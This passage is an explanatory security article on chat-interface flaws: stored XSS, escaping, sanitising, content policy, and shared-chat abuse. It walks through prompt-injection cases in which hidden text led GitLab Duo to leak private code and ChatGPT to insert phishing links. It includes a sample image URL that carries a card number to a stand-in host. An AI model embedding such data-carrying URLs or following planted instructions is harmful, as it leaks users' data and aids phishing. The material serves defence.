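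The researchers found the flaw on 22 July 2025 and told Lenovo that day. Lenovo acknowledged the report on 6 August and had mitigated the problem by 18 August, according to ITPro's *Flaw in Lenovo’s customer service AI chatbot*. Lenovo's public statement mentions "corrective actions" without describing them, so it is unclear whether the company changed how the agents' software displays replies or only instructed or trained Lena to refuse such requests. A better-worded message could still get past Lena's refusals, whereas a change to the display would work regardless of wording.

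Lenovo could also have marked its session cookies as HttpOnly, a setting that stops scripts in a page from reading them. The cookies the researchers captured can't have had this setting. HttpOnly limits the damage but doesn't remove the flaw, since a hostile script can still send requests from the agent's open page.

### A WordPress chat log, repaired twice

Small sites have had the same problem in their logs, with no model involved. WPBot, the WordPress plugin that let anonymous visitors submit invented conversations, has a few thousand installations, according to Patchstack's *ChatBot*. ProjectDiscovery's *WPBot <= 8.4.9* (2026) explains that the plugin saved the conversation and displayed it to the administrator without sanitising it at either step. Wordfence's *WPBot <= 8.4.9* (2026) lists 8.5.0 as the fixed version.

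The flaw was listed again ten weeks later. Lutra Security's *WPBot <= 8.7.3* (2026) describes stored XSS through the same field in every version up to 8.7.3, so owners who had installed the first repair were exposed. The plugin also still printed its access code on every public page. Wordfence's *WPBot*, a running list of the plugin's flaws, marks this one as patched too. The entries don't explain why the first repair was insufficient.

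An owner in this position needs to know which step the developer repaired. If the plugin now cleans messages as they arrive, any script saved before the update may still run when someone opens an old conversation. If the plugin escapes messages as it displays them, the old ones become harmless too. WPScan blames the similar flaw in GeekyBot on failures at both steps.

### Why deleting tags fails

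Many developers first try to solve the problem by deleting anything that looks like a tag. A simple tag stripper removes every `<`, the next `>` and whatever lies between them. Suppose a visitor to the library's site asks:

`is 3 < 5 and 7 > 2?`

The stripper finds a `<` after the 3 and a `>` after the 7, and deletes everything from one to the other. The page then shows:

`is 3 2?`

The question contained no HTML. A browser would not have treated `< 5` as a tag, because a tag's name must begin with a letter and directly follow the `<`. The stripper used a cruder rule and damaged the question. If it ran before the server saved the text, nobody can recover the original, and the model may have answered the damaged version.

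Escaping changes the same question to:

`is 3 &lt; 5 and 7 &gt; 2?`

The browser displays `&lt;` as `<` and `&gt;` as `>`, so the reader sees exactly what the visitor typed.

Stripping is also unreliable as a defence. Take a filter that searches for the three characters `<b>` and deletes them, and give it this text:

`<<b>b>`

The filter removes the `<b>` in the middle, and the characters on either side join to form another `<b>`. Bold type is harmless, but the same trick works on a filter that looks for dangerous tags. The developer can prevent this by repeating the deletion until nothing changes. Repetition doesn't help with a tag that the attacker leaves unfinished, because the filter finds no closing `>` to match, while the browser treats the next `>` in the page's own code as the end of the tag.

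Some attacks contain no tag, so a tag stripper finds nothing to remove. CleanTalk, a security company, describes an older flaw of this kind in WPBot's FAQ editor. The plugin placed the question inside an attribute, the part of a tag that holds a setting between quotation marks. A quotation mark in the question ended the setting early, and the browser read the next words as a new attribute containing a script, which ran when someone moved the mouse over the text. The risk was small because only a user with considerable privileges could enter such a question.

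### Escaping for the place where the text appears

These are the treatments for some common destinations:

| Where the text goes | What the site should do |
|---|---|
| Body of a page | Convert `&`, `<` and `>` |
| Attribute | Put the value in quotation marks, and convert any quotation marks inside it as well |
| Address of a link | Accept only approved kinds of address, such as `https`, then escape it as an attribute |
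| Data inside a script | Encode it as JSON, and write each `<` as `\u003c` so that the text cannot close the script element |
| Spreadsheet export | Stop the program from reading text that starts with `=` as a formula |

Link addresses need a separate check because an address that starts with `javascript:` instead of `https:` can contain a script, and escaping doesn't change that prefix. WordPress has a function for each of the most common cases: `esc_html` for body text, `esc_attr` for attributes and `esc_url` for addresses.

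A developer must also convert `&` first, and escape the text only once. Converting `&` last would turn `&lt;` into `&amp;lt;`, so readers would see `&lt;` instead of `<`. Page templates in systems such as Django and React escape text automatically, which avoids both mistakes. The danger comes from bypassing this escaping, which React allows through `dangerouslySetInnerHTML`. Developers of chat windows are tempted to use it because they want bold type and links in the answers.

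It is better to store the original message and escape each copy for its destination, since the same question may later go to a web page, a staff log, an email and a spreadsheet. Cybernews instead recommends sanitising content before storing it and accepting only approved characters from visitors. A list of approved characters works well for an order number, but a help desk for beginners has to accept questions about `<b>`. The server should still limit length and check identifiers when a message arrives.

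OWASP's guidance on model output extends the same principle beyond web pages. If a model's answer goes into a database command, the developer should use a parameterised query. If it goes to a program that runs commands, as it might in a coding assistant, the application has to validate it first. OWASP also recommends logging the output and monitoring it for unusual patterns. The page where staff read those logs will show strangers' text, so it needs the same escaping as the public pages.

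Plain text is enough for most staff logs. An administrator reviewing a conversation needs to see what the visitor typed and what the model replied, and escaped text shows this more accurately than formatted text, including any tags an attacker tried to use.

### Formatted answers

Lists, bold type and links in the chat window help customers. To display this formatting, the site has to allow some HTML, which it should sanitise only after converting the model's Markdown.

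The library's answer shows why Markdown should be converted before it is sanitised. The model writes the tag `<b>` between backticks, which mark computer code in Markdown. The converter escapes the tag and marks it as code, so the sanitiser leaves it alone. If the sanitiser runs first, it doesn't parse the backticks. It treats `<b>` as a real tag and, if bold type is not on its list of allowed tags, deletes it from the sentence. Sanitising first is also unsafe. A Markdown link consists of brackets and an address, which a sanitiser treats as ordinary text, so a hostile address passes through and the converter turns it into a working link.

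The approved list for a help desk can be limited to paragraphs, lists, bold and italic type, code, and links with an `https` address. Images need a stricter rule because the browser contacts an image's address as soon as it displays the answer. A sanitiser will still allow an ordinary link to a scam website. A site like Eurostar's could avoid this by having the model choose a help article by number and having the site's own code write the link. The model would then not need to produce HTML, and a visitor could at worst get a link to the wrong article.

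DOMPurify, a free JavaScript library from the German security company Cure53, is a common choice for sanitising HTML. It passes the HTML to the browser's parser, which builds a tree of elements without displaying them. DOMPurify then removes every element and attribute that is not on its list of allowed ones, and converts the rest back to text. Using the browser's parser avoids the tag stripper's mistake of reading HTML by different rules from the browser. The default list allows a lot, so a help desk should replace it with its own.

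DOMPurify's weak point is the conversion back to text. The page has to parse that text again to display it, and in rare cases the second parsing produces a different tree from the one DOMPurify checked. An attacker can use the difference to get a script past the check, a method called mutation XSS. Researchers have found several such bypasses and the maintainers have fixed them, so an old copy of the library is a risk. A site that runs DOMPurify on its server also depends on a substitute for the browser's parser, which must be up to date too.

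Browsers have begun to offer a built-in alternative, the HTML Sanitizer API. A developer calls `setHTML` on the part of the page that should hold the answer, and the browser parses the HTML, removes what is not allowed and inserts the remaining tree directly. The tree is never turned back into text, so there is no second parse for an attacker to exploit. `setHTML` always removes scripts and the attributes that run them, even if the developer has allowed them. A companion function, `setHTMLUnsafe`, does not guarantee this.

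Firefox 148 was the first browser to ship the API in its current form, in February 2026, and Chrome 146 followed in March. Safari did not support it then. A public site therefore still needs DOMPurify for browsers without `setHTML`, and its code can check which one to use. The API works only in a browser, so it can't clean an answer that the server sends by email.

### The policy behind the page

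A content security policy can limit the damage when a developer forgets to escape something. The server might send this one with the page that support agents use:

`default-src 'self'; object-src 'none'; base-uri 'none'; form-action 'self'`

The first rule lets the page load scripts and images only from the site's own server, and connect only to that server. It also blocks scripts written into the page, including those attached to an image. On Lenovo's support page, this would have stopped the browser from running the script when the image failed to load. If a script had run another way, the same rule would have blocked a background connection to the researchers' server. The last rule stops a fake login form from sending an agent's password elsewhere.

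Such a policy is harder to add to an existing site, because many pages rely on scripts written into their HTML. Developers often respond by adding the setting `'unsafe-inline'`, which permits all such scripts and would have allowed the code in Lenovo's image to run. It is safer to mark each legitimate script with a nonce, a random value that the server changes every time it sends the page, so that an attacker who stores a script can't know the value it will need later.

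Developers can first send the policy in report-only mode, in which the browser reports violations without blocking them. The reports show which of the site's own scripts need changing, but the policy gives no protection in the meantime. Even an enforced policy can fail if an attacker finds a way to serve code from a listed source, and it does not stop an agent from clicking an ordinary link in a convincing answer.

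## Links and images in answers: GitLab Duo and ChatGPT page summaries

A chatbot's answer can do harm even after a sanitiser has removed every script. An image can send private data to a stranger as soon as the answer appears, and a link can lead to a fake login page that the assistant seems to endorse. Researchers demonstrated both with GitLab Duo, a coding assistant, in 2025. A year later, another team showed that whoever writes a web page could place links and images in ChatGPT's summary of it.

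### How an image address carries data

A model adds an image to an answer by writing the image's address, and the browser requests the picture from the server at that address. The request includes the whole address, which the server's owner can record. Addresses often end with extra text after a question mark, for ordinary purposes such as choosing the size of a picture. Suppose a visitor has told the library's assistant a card number, and the answer includes an image with this address:

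`https://images.example/cat.png?card=20417`

Whoever runs images.example now has the card number. The visitor may see a picture of a cat, or nothing if the picture is a single transparent pixel.

The visitor has no reason to ask for such an image, but an indirect injection could make the model add one with something from the conversation in its URL. Even an image with a fixed URL reveals the visitor's IP address, browser type and the time of the request.

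A link can carry data in the same way, but normally sends it only if someone clicks. PromptArmor's *Threat Intelligence* explains that messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch previews of links, so a link an assistant writes there can send its data without a click.

The security researcher Johann Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023. According to his Embrace The Red blog post, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Microsoft used a content security policy to block most images in Bing Chat that May, and OpenAI added a check on addresses in December. Rehberger later found ways around OpenAI's check and found that the macOS and iOS apps lacked it.

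### GitLab Duo

GitLab hosts software projects, many of them public. Its assistant, Duo, ran on Anthropic's Claude and helped programmers understand code and review merge requests (proposed changes to a project). To answer a question, Duo read everything on the page, including comments and code that strangers had written.

Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* describes how the security company's researchers planted instructions in descriptions, comments, commit messages (notes attached to code changes) and the code itself. Duo followed the instructions wherever they appeared. The researchers also found ways to hide them from human readers, such as white text and invisible Unicode characters.

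The hidden text could make Duo recommend a malicious software package, describe a dangerous merge request as safe, or present a link to a fake login page as legitimate. A programmer who would ignore such a claim in a stranger's comment might believe it from GitLab's own assistant.

The theft of private code relied on Duo being able to read whatever the person asking could read, including private projects. The researchers hid an instruction in a merge request on a public project, and a user playing the victim asked Duo an ordinary question about the file. Duo followed the instruction and read a merge request in a private project. It then encoded the changes as base64, a format that represents any data in ordinary characters, and added the result to an image address. The victim's browser requested the image, which sent the code to the researchers' server.

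Legit Security says the same method could have exposed confidential reports of unpatched security flaws, but the company's published demonstration covers only code. The attacker would also have needed to know the address of the private merge request, because the hidden text included it.

Willison's short commentary, *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*, identifies three conditions behind the attack: access to private information, exposure to untrusted text, and a way to send data out. Removing any one of them prevents the theft. GitLab could not easily keep untrusted text from an assistant that reviews strangers' code, so it blocked the way to send data out.

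Legit Security reported the problem on 12 February 2025 and published its account on 22 May, after GitLab had confirmed the fixes. Duo no longer displays elements such as images and forms that point outside gitlab.com. An image address on gitlab.com is useless to an attacker who can't read GitLab's server logs. GitLab also said that it had fixed the prompt injection, but Legit Security doesn't explain how. It also doesn't mention any restriction on ordinary links, so it is unclear whether hidden text could still make Duo recommend a fake login page.

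### Markup that arrives in pieces

GitLab was already using DOMPurify, which stopped the researchers from running a script. DOMPurify let the image through because its default list of approved elements includes images, forms and links.

The way Duo displayed its answers also helped the attack. Most chat windows stream answers, showing each piece as it arrives from the model. The researchers saw a word change style while Duo was still writing and realised that Duo was converting Markdown to HTML before it had the whole answer.

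In the library's answer about `<b>`, for example, the model puts the tag between two backticks. For a moment, the chat window has received the first backtick and the tag but not the second. A lone backtick has no special meaning in Markdown, so a converter that permits HTML treats `<b>` as a real tag. It corrects the mistake when the second backtick arrives, and the visitor sees at most a flicker of bold type. If the tag had been for an image, the browser might have requested the image before the correction.

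Sanitising each fragment separately also misses tags that are split between fragments. If one fragment ends with `<` and the next begins with `b>`, the complete tag appears only when they are joined. The sanitiser therefore has to examine the whole answer so far.

Legit Security's researchers got their HTML displayed by putting it in a link's label. They attribute the flaw to the browser interpreting the HTML before proper sanitising took effect. That explains how text could become live markup, but it can't fully explain the leak, because DOMPurify was running and its list of allowed elements included images. Sanitising the finished answer with the same list would probably have let the image through too.

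A chat window can stream answers safely if, at each update, it converts and sanitises all the text received so far before changing the page. The developer should also turn off HTML in the Markdown converter, so that any tag the model writes appears as text. The window should not load images until the answer is complete and the site has checked their addresses.

Converting all the text received so far each time a new piece arrives takes more computing. For an answer that arrives in 1,000 equal pieces, the page processes about 500 times as much text as it would by converting the answer once. Updating the display less often reduces the work. A small site could instead show plain text during streaming and add the formatting at the end, so visitors would see no bold type or links for a few seconds.

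*The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, from trackr.live, attributes SearchLeak, a 2026 flaw in another company's product, to a race similar to GitLab's between displaying streamed HTML and sanitising it.

### ChatGPT's summaries of web pages

Firefox lets people send the page they are reading to ChatGPT for a summary. Andi Ahmeti of the security company Permiso used this feature to demonstrate an attack that the company named ChatGPhish. Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, published on 29 May 2026, describes three versions of the attack.

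In the first, Ahmeti added instructions to a GitHub project's description that required every response to contain a normal summary followed by a notice that a new device had been added to the reader's account. ChatGPT wrote both, and the notice included a working link to a site Ahmeti had chosen. Nothing in the reply showed that the notice came from the page's author, and the accurate summary above it probably made it more believable.

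The second version put a QR code in the notice, using an image stored on Amazon's servers. Scanning the code opens the link on a phone, so the desktop browser cannot warn about the address and its password manager cannot detect the wrong domain. The third version loaded an image through a link-shortening service and recorded the reader's IP address, browser details and the time of the answer. The attack also worked on an ordinary web page hosted by Permiso, so it did not depend on GitHub. Permiso does not blame Firefox, which only passed the page's text to ChatGPT.

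Permiso's reports to OpenAI described the problem as both a data leak and phishing, but the evidence for phishing is stronger. The published tests leaked details about the reader's connection, but not the conversation or account data. Permiso gives no success rate, so the tests show that the attack is possible but not how reliably it works. CloudEagle's *ChatGPhish* (2026) offers some independent support, reporting that the technology news site The Register reproduced the behaviour on the day of publication.

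Permiso reported the problem on 29 April through OpenAI's reward programme. The next day OpenAI marked the report as not reproducible, citing a lack of detail. Permiso sent a fuller version on 1 May, which was first labelled "Not Applicable" and later marked as a duplicate of an earlier report. On 7 May Permiso asked to discuss the wider impact further, and it published its findings three weeks later.

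These labels are the only response from OpenAI that Permiso records. A duplicate label suggests that OpenAI already knew of the problem, but does not show whether it planned a fix. Expert Insights' *ChatGPT Can Be Tricked Into Delivering Phishing Links From Any Web Page* says that the outlet had asked OpenAI for comment. Permiso reports no fix, and OpenAI does not appear to have announced one by early December 2026.

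### Which addresses to allow

The safest rule is to load no images from other servers, which a site can enforce through its content security policy. The library would lose little. A shop could still show its own product photographs if the model chose them by number, as with Eurostar's help articles.

Some sites use an image proxy, a server of their own that fetches the picture and passes it to the visitor. The picture's host sees the proxy's IP address instead of the visitor's, but it still receives the full image address, including any private data the model has added. A proxy prevents that leak only if it saves its pictures in advance, for example when a customer posts a review, and refuses any new address that appears in an answer. Without this restriction, it also lets strangers choose which addresses the site's server connects to.

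GitLab's solution, a list of approved domains, works well when the list contains only the company's own site, but longer lists are less reliable. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that many reputable sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a request that starts at an approved domain can end at an attacker's server. Shared hosting causes a similar problem. Permiso's QR code was on Amazon's storage service, where anyone can rent space, and a site that approved the whole service would have displayed it. Strict lists also produce frequent warnings, and OpenAI worries that people will learn to click through them.

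OpenAI instead checks the complete address. Its crawler, which collects public web pages and has no access to anyone's conversations, keeps an index of addresses. ChatGPT can automatically load an address already in the index, because an address that existed before the conversation is unlikely to contain a secret from it. For any other address, ChatGPT looks for an alternative or shows the user a warning.

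An attacker can still use public addresses as a code. Rehberger describes a method with 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit. With hostile instructions, the attacker gets the model to spell out a secret by opening the page for each character in turn, then reads the sequence in the server's log. A six-digit login code would take six requests. A choice among *N* pages conveys log₂ *N* bits, so each request carries about 5 bits with 36 pages and 12 bits with 4,096. Rehberger suggests ChatGPT should either refuse to fetch the same address twice in a session or reuse a saved copy. This would make long messages harder to send but would not stop short ones. He still considers OpenAI's check a significant improvement.

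The check offers much less protection against ChatGPhish. A QR code with a fixed address contains nothing from the conversation, and that address can be in the index like any other. OpenAI had warned in January that the check doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of attempts to manipulate the reader. This may explain why Permiso's report was at one stage marked "Not Applicable", although OpenAI has not published its reasons.

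Links are harder to restrict because people need them. A chat window can show the destination's domain beside each link, so readers can see when an account warning leads to an unfamiliar site. This adds clutter, and it doesn't help with QR codes or readers who don't know which domain is genuine. Labelling text that came from a summarised page would also help, but the application can't do this reliably once the model has blended that text into its own answer.

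A public assistant can usually be stricter than ChatGPT because its job is narrower. The library could allow links only to its own pages, but then its assistant couldn't link a visitor to the bus timetable.

### Lockdown Mode and its bypass

OpenAI offers people with sensitive data an optional setting, Lockdown Mode, that removes many of the ways data could leak. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it for large organisations in February, and the company extended it to personal accounts from 4 June. The setting switches features off by fixed rules, so an injection can't make the model switch them back on.

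OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* lists what the setting restricts. ChatGPT can read only saved copies of web pages, which may be out of date. It does not retrieve images from the web and may not show images in ordinary answers. It cannot download files for analysis, and code written in its Canvas editor cannot connect to the network. Deep research and agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out longer tasks on the web, are unavailable. OpenAI says that most people do not need the setting, and these restrictions are a good reason not to impose it on everyone.

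Lockdown Mode doesn't prevent prompt injection, so hostile text in an uploaded file or a saved web page can still change an answer. The setting should stop ChatGPhish's QR code and tracking image, but the list of restrictions doesn't mention ordinary links, so a false security alert could presumably still contain one. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, nevertheless welcomed the setting, which limits ways to send data out, the third of his conditions.

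In June, OpenAI described prompt injection in its FAQ as "not currently a major risk", The Decoder reported. By early December, the help page described it as a known security risk for systems that process untrusted content.

Researchers at Check Point, a security company, found a way around Lockdown Mode through a feature that the mode did not restrict. ChatGPT can preview a web page whose HTML appears in a code block. Because that HTML may contain scripts, ChatGPT runs it in a sandbox, a frame that cannot read ChatGPT's cookies or contact other servers without the user's consent.

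The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) quotes Check Point's explanation of the flaw. ChatGPT intercepted the previewed page's attempts to open a new window, but the sandbox's settings allowed new windows and let them open without its restrictions. The page could create a frame inside itself that had its own copy of the browser's function for opening windows, which ChatGPT had not modified. A window opened from that frame could send text from the chat to an attacker's server. It could also display a fake ChatGPT update that installed malicious software.

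In the desktop app, the attack could steal data without any click. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* explains that the new window could appear there without any user action. OpenAI fixed the flaw on its own servers on 18 September 2026, so users did not have to install anything. Check Point tested the fix and confirmed that it worked, according to *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026). The published accounts do not specify what OpenAI changed. The more robust fix would be to remove the sandbox's permission to open windows, because the browser enforces that rule in every frame the page creates.

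Check Point said the hostile HTML could reach a victim through a crafted prompt, a customised version of ChatGPT or a shared chat. A week before Check Point published, other researchers had described a separate flaw in the same preview feature. An attacker could exploit that flaw by sending someone a link to a shared conversation.

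## Shared ChatGPT conversations as public web pages

When a ChatGPT user presses "Share", OpenAI copies the conversation to a web page that anyone with the link can open. On personal accounts, the page shows the conversation as it stood when the user created or last updated the link, according to OpenAI's *Sharing conversations and scheduled tasks in ChatGPT*. Sharing therefore lets strangers publish text they wrote or prompted at an address that begins with chatgpt.com, and OpenAI mentions no review before the page goes live.

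Since 2025, people have accidentally published private matters through ChatGPT's sharing feature, and criminals have used it to spread malware. In October 2026, researchers showed that opening a shared chat could give a stranger control of the reader's account.

### Private chats in search results

Until late April 2025, OpenAI told users that search engines did not index shared links. It then added a box to the share window labelled "Make this chat discoverable". Windows Central's *ChatGPT chats won’t show up on Google anymore* quotes archived copies of OpenAI's help page from 26 and 28 April, before and after the change. According to a news report quoted by David (2025) in *ChatGPT users shocked to learn their chats were in Google search results*, a caveat that the chat could appear in search results was under the box in smaller, lighter type. Someone sending a chat to a colleague could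 easily have ticked the box, thinking the colleague would need it to find the page.

On 31 July the business magazine Fast Company reported that about 4,500 shared chats had appeared in Google search results, some of them about mental health or relationships. PYMNTS's *ChatGPT Users May Be Inadvertently Sharing Conversations in Search Results* explains that the magazine found them by searching for part of the address that shared links have in common. OpenAI first defended the label as "sufficiently clear". The same day, its chief information security officer, Dane Stuckey, announced that the company was removing the option because it gave people too many chances to share things by accident. OpenAI also began asking search engines to remove the pages from their results.

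A researcher had collected nearly 100,000 indexed chats, far more than the first count, and they included confidential contracts, according to 404 Media's *Nearly 100,000 ChatGPT Conversations Were Searchable on Google*. Digital Digging's *ChatGPT Confessions gone?* (2025) reported that OpenAI had cleared nearly 50,000 from Google's index. But The Irish Times' *Thousands of ChatGPT conversations accessible online despite efforts to erase them* (2025) relayed that more than 100,000 were still accessible because the Internet Archive's Wayback Machine had saved copies. The Wayback Machine's director said OpenAI had not asked for their removal, according to Wccftech.

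None of these figures measures how many people shared a chat by mistake. Some people presumably ticked the box because they wanted readers, and the archive can save any page whose address it has, whether or not the owner ticked the box. The archive also held other companies' chats. A report in the AI Incident Database describes collecting 143,142 readable share links for several chatbots from the archive's index.

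The HTML of archived ChatGPT chats also contained an IP address, as Hakan (2025) reports in *The Curious Case of ChatGPT-share*. A colleague's test showed that it belonged to whoever was viewing the page, not to the person who had shared it. The addresses in the archived copies seemed to be the archive's own, so they exposed nobody. But a reader who saved a chat and reposted the file might have published their own IP address.

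The share button in Grok, the chatbot from Elon Musk's company xAI, published each chat on a page open to search engines, without a checkbox or a warning. Search engines indexed more than 370,000 of these chats. Nolan (2025), in *Thousands of private user conversations with Elon Musk’s Grok AI chatbot*, reports that they included medical questions, business details and at least one password. According to PC Gamer, users had been warning about this since at least January 2025, seven months before the press covered it. Meta's AI app posted shared chats to a public feed called Discover, and Google indexed those too. Many users didn't realise they were posting to a feed.

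### An instruction that Google could not read

In July 2026, Reddit users found shared Claude chats in Google search results. TechSpot's *Hundreds of shared Claude chats, including resumes and health details* reports that at least 200 came up. According to Axios' *Users' Claude creations are showing up in Google search* (2026), Anthropic said a chat becomes searchable only after somebody posts its link where a search engine can see it, such as on a forum.

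Google listed the shared Claude chats because two of Anthropic's instructions conflicted, according to Search Engine Journal's *Indexed Claude Chats Show Why Disallow Is Not Noindex*. Anthropic sent the pages with a "noindex" instruction, which tells search engines not to list them. It also blocked the pages in its robots.txt file, which tells crawlers which addresses not to fetch. Google's crawler therefore never fetched the pages and never received the noindex instruction. Google can still list an address it has not fetched if another site links to it.

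The remedy is to allow the crawler to access the page so that it can read the noindex instruction. Search Engine Journal checked on 27 July but could not establish whether that instruction was there when Google first found the chats, so the conflict is a likely but unproven cause.

By then the chats had disappeared from the results. Nolan (2026) found in *A trove of users’ seemingly private conversations with Anthropic’s Claude AI chatbot* that many of the links still worked for anyone who had them. A search engine can stop listing a page, but only the site or the person who shared the chat can take the page down.

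The Grok episode had also attracted marketers. Forbes reported that they were discussing how to script chats that mentioned their products, hoping the site's standing with Google would help the pages appear in search results. It was unclear whether this would work, since Google might treat the pages as spam.

### Shared chats that installed malware

Criminals have also used shared chats to spread malware. The security company Huntress reported a case in which the top Google result was a shared ChatGPT chat that spread Mac malware. Kaspersky documented shared ChatGPT chats that delivered Atomic macOS Stealer, a program that steals data from Macs. Others found Claude chats presented as an installation guide from "Apple Support". *LLMShare* (Maharaj, 2026), a report for the security company Push Security, summarises the Kaspersky and Claude cases.

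In both, the chat contained a command for the reader to paste into the terminal, a window for typing instructions to the computer. The command downloaded and ran the attacker's program. Sanitising the page would not have helped, because the command was plain text, and the browser could not block a program that the reader started outside it. The request didn't look odd, because people install many genuine AI tools by pasting a command. Maharaj argues that this has accustomed inexperienced users to doing so.

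A shared chat makes such a command look like the assistant's advice. ChatGPT also lets a user share one response without the rest of the conversation, so readers see the answer but not the prompts that produced it.

ChatGPT's canvas feature lets a user build a small interactive page and share it. In January 2026, before anyone had reported attackers using these pages, Yasin Tas of Eye Security tested what attackers might do with them. *From Helper to Adversary* (Tas, 2026) describes his first attempt, a fake login form. When he pressed the button to submit a password, ChatGPT asked permission to connect to an outside address and warned against allowing it if the address was unfamiliar. Tas expected most people to refuse.

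He then built a fake staff survey with an "I'm not a robot" box. Ticking the box copied a command to the clipboard, and the page displayed instructions to paste it into a Windows dialog that runs programs. The trick needed no connection from the canvas, so no warning appeared. OpenAI ruled his report outside its reward programme because it concerned phishing rather than a technical flaw.

Tas also compared how the companies labelled such pages. Google's Gemini covered the page with a warning that another person had made it, which visitors had to dismiss before continuing. Tas thought this would make most people leave, but he did not test it with users. ChatGPT put a small note at the top. Claude refused to write the harmful version, though Tas thought repeated attempts might succeed.

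### A fake outage notice on chatgpt.com

Four months later, Push Security found criminals using such a page. The company named the technique LLMShare and published its account on 29 May 2026. The victims searched for "chatgpt", "chatgpt free" or a misspelling such as "chatgot", then clicked an advertisement at the top of the results that led to a real chatgpt.com address.

The shared page resembled a message from OpenAI. It claimed that the website was unavailable because of heavy traffic and offered a desktop app instead. The attacker had written the notice in HTML and CSS (the code that sets a page's appearance), and ChatGPT displayed it as a finished page. The download button led to a copy of OpenAI's download page on the attacker's own domain. VirusTotal, which checks files with many antivirus programs, flagged the Windows and Mac programs offered there as malicious. eWEEK's *ChatGPT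 Share Links Abused Through Real OpenAI URLs* (2026) reports that it was unclear what the programs ultimately did, and reports no sign that anyone had broken into OpenAI.

Many security products decide whether to block a page by checking its domain's reputation. This works when one organisation writes everything on the domain. The products rated chatgpt.com as safe because OpenAI runs it, and they gave the same rating to a page that a criminal had written there. People use the same shortcut, and a careful reader who checked the address in the advertisement would have seen ChatGPT's real address.

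OpenAI's advice did not help much. In June, OpenAI's *ChatGPT Shared Links FAQ* stated that shared links start with `chatgpt.com/share/`, but the fake notice's address started with `chatgpt.com/s/`. A reader who knew the rule might have become suspicious, but someone who had clicked on an advertisement for ChatGPT had no reason to think of shared links. OpenAI now lists `/s/` as the form for shared scheduled tasks. It advises people to check that a link is on chatgpt.com, as the fake notice was, and that they trust whoever sent it.

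The attacker's download site was on an ordinary domain that security products could have blocked. To delay blocking, the attacker showed visitors different pages depending on who they were. When Push's researchers submitted the address to an automated scanner, it recorded the website of a harmless virtual reality company. The attacker could also replace a blocked download site and edit or replace the notice to point to the new one.

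ChatGPT displayed two buttons above the fake notice, "Show code" and "Remix with ChatGPT", which the attacker could not remove. A real outage notice would not have them, and pressing the first showed the HTML behind the page. The buttons were a warning to readers who already knew that ChatGPT hosts pages its users make. Other readers could not tell from the words "Show code" that a stranger had written the message or that OpenAI had not checked it. Reading the code wouldn't necessarily have helped either, since it contained only a polite notice and a link.

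Push sells a browser security product that it says blocks these pages, so it benefits if customers find the threat alarming. Its screenshots and the addresses it published are good evidence that the campaign existed. It doesn't say how many people visited the pages or how many infections resulted, only that it detected the pages at several customers. Its researchers also had trouble getting the advertisements to appear again, and attributed this to the attacker limiting them to certain places or times.

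### A shared chat that took over accounts

LLMShare required its victims to download and run a program. In October 2026, researchers at the security firm Parameter carried out an attack that only required a signed-in user to open their shared chat. *Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) explains how the attack worked.

The attack began with the same HTML preview that Check Point had used to get around Lockdown Mode. OpenAI runs the preview's sandbox on a different web address from the main page. Browsers prevent a script from reading a page at another address unless that page allows it, so the preview cannot read the ChatGPT page around it. The sandbox worked this time, and the weakness was in the surrounding ChatGPT page.

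Pages that can't read each other can still exchange messages through a browser function called `postMessage`. The receiving page should check who sent a message before acting on it. To help display graphs, ChatGPT used a library called MathLive, which has an on-screen keyboard for typing mathematics. Whenever a chat contained an interactive graph, MathLive listened in the main ChatGPT page for messages about this keyboard and accepted them from any address.

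The researchers' preview sent two messages. The first replaced the keyboard's layout, which could contain HTML, with the researchers' own HTML. The second made MathLive show the keyboard, and MathLive inserted the HTML into the main page. The HTML first went through a function called `createHTML`, which only marked it as trusted, although it looked as if it might sanitise it.

This alone could not run a script, because browsers don't run script elements inserted this way. The researchers instead inserted a frame with its contents written into one of its attributes. A frame created inside the preview would have inherited the preview's restrictions, but the main page created this one without a `sandbox` attribute, so the browser treated it as part of chatgpt.com.

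ChatGPT's content security policy, the last obstacle, blocked scripts written into the frame but allowed scripts from YouTube. One YouTube address returns information about a video as a script that calls a function named by the requester. The researchers sent code in place of the name. YouTube returned an error message saying the name was invalid, but put the code before it in the reply, and the browser ran the code.

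The researchers needed several attempts to fit all this into one link. The first version required the victim to connect an app the researchers controlled. The second used an HTML file attached to the chat, but ChatGPT left the graph out of the public copy, so nothing loaded MathLive. In the final version, the conversation contained a real graph followed by HTML the model had written. The most reliable form required the victim to click "Preview" once. Later the researchers got the preview to open by itself, about four and a half seconds after the page opened. This worked three times in a separate account.

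The script listed the victim's conversations, read one that the victim had never shared, and sent part of it to the researchers' server. It sent the text by adding it to an image address, according to *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts* (Willison, 2026), the same method used to steal code through GitLab Duo. Goyal adds that the script could have done anything the account's owner could do on the site. That is a reasonable inference, since the script could call the same functions as ChatGPT's own page, but the researchers demonstrated only reading and sending. *A Shared ChatGPT Link Could Run Attacker Code in Your Session* (The Hacker News, 2026) notes that they used test accounts and reported no use by criminals.

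They reported the flaw on 18 October. OpenAI reproduced it three days later and raised its severity to P1, the highest level. KIberblick's *ChatGPT* (2026) lists a partial fix on 22 and 23 October, which included a change to the content security policy. It lists a complete fix on 26 October, when both versions of ChatGPT's web page began rejecting the messages. OpenAI paid $5,000, which Willison thought "a bit cheap for a vulnerability this serious".

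Removing YouTube from the policy would have stopped this script but not fixed the main fault. As The Hacker News points out, a preview could still have inserted HTML into the real ChatGPT page. An attacker might have used that to show a fake login form, which needs no script.

OpenAI had made a similar mistake before. Hacktron's researchers found that OpenAI's forum would open a web address sent to it in a message from any other page. An address can contain a script, so this also let an attacker run code on an OpenAI site.

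### Separating strangers' pages from the main site

A site that runs strangers' HTML should check both the address and the frame that each message comes from. If the library let beginners share small practice pages, its code might begin like this:

```
window.addEventListener("message", (event) => {
  if (event.origin !== "https://practice.example") return;
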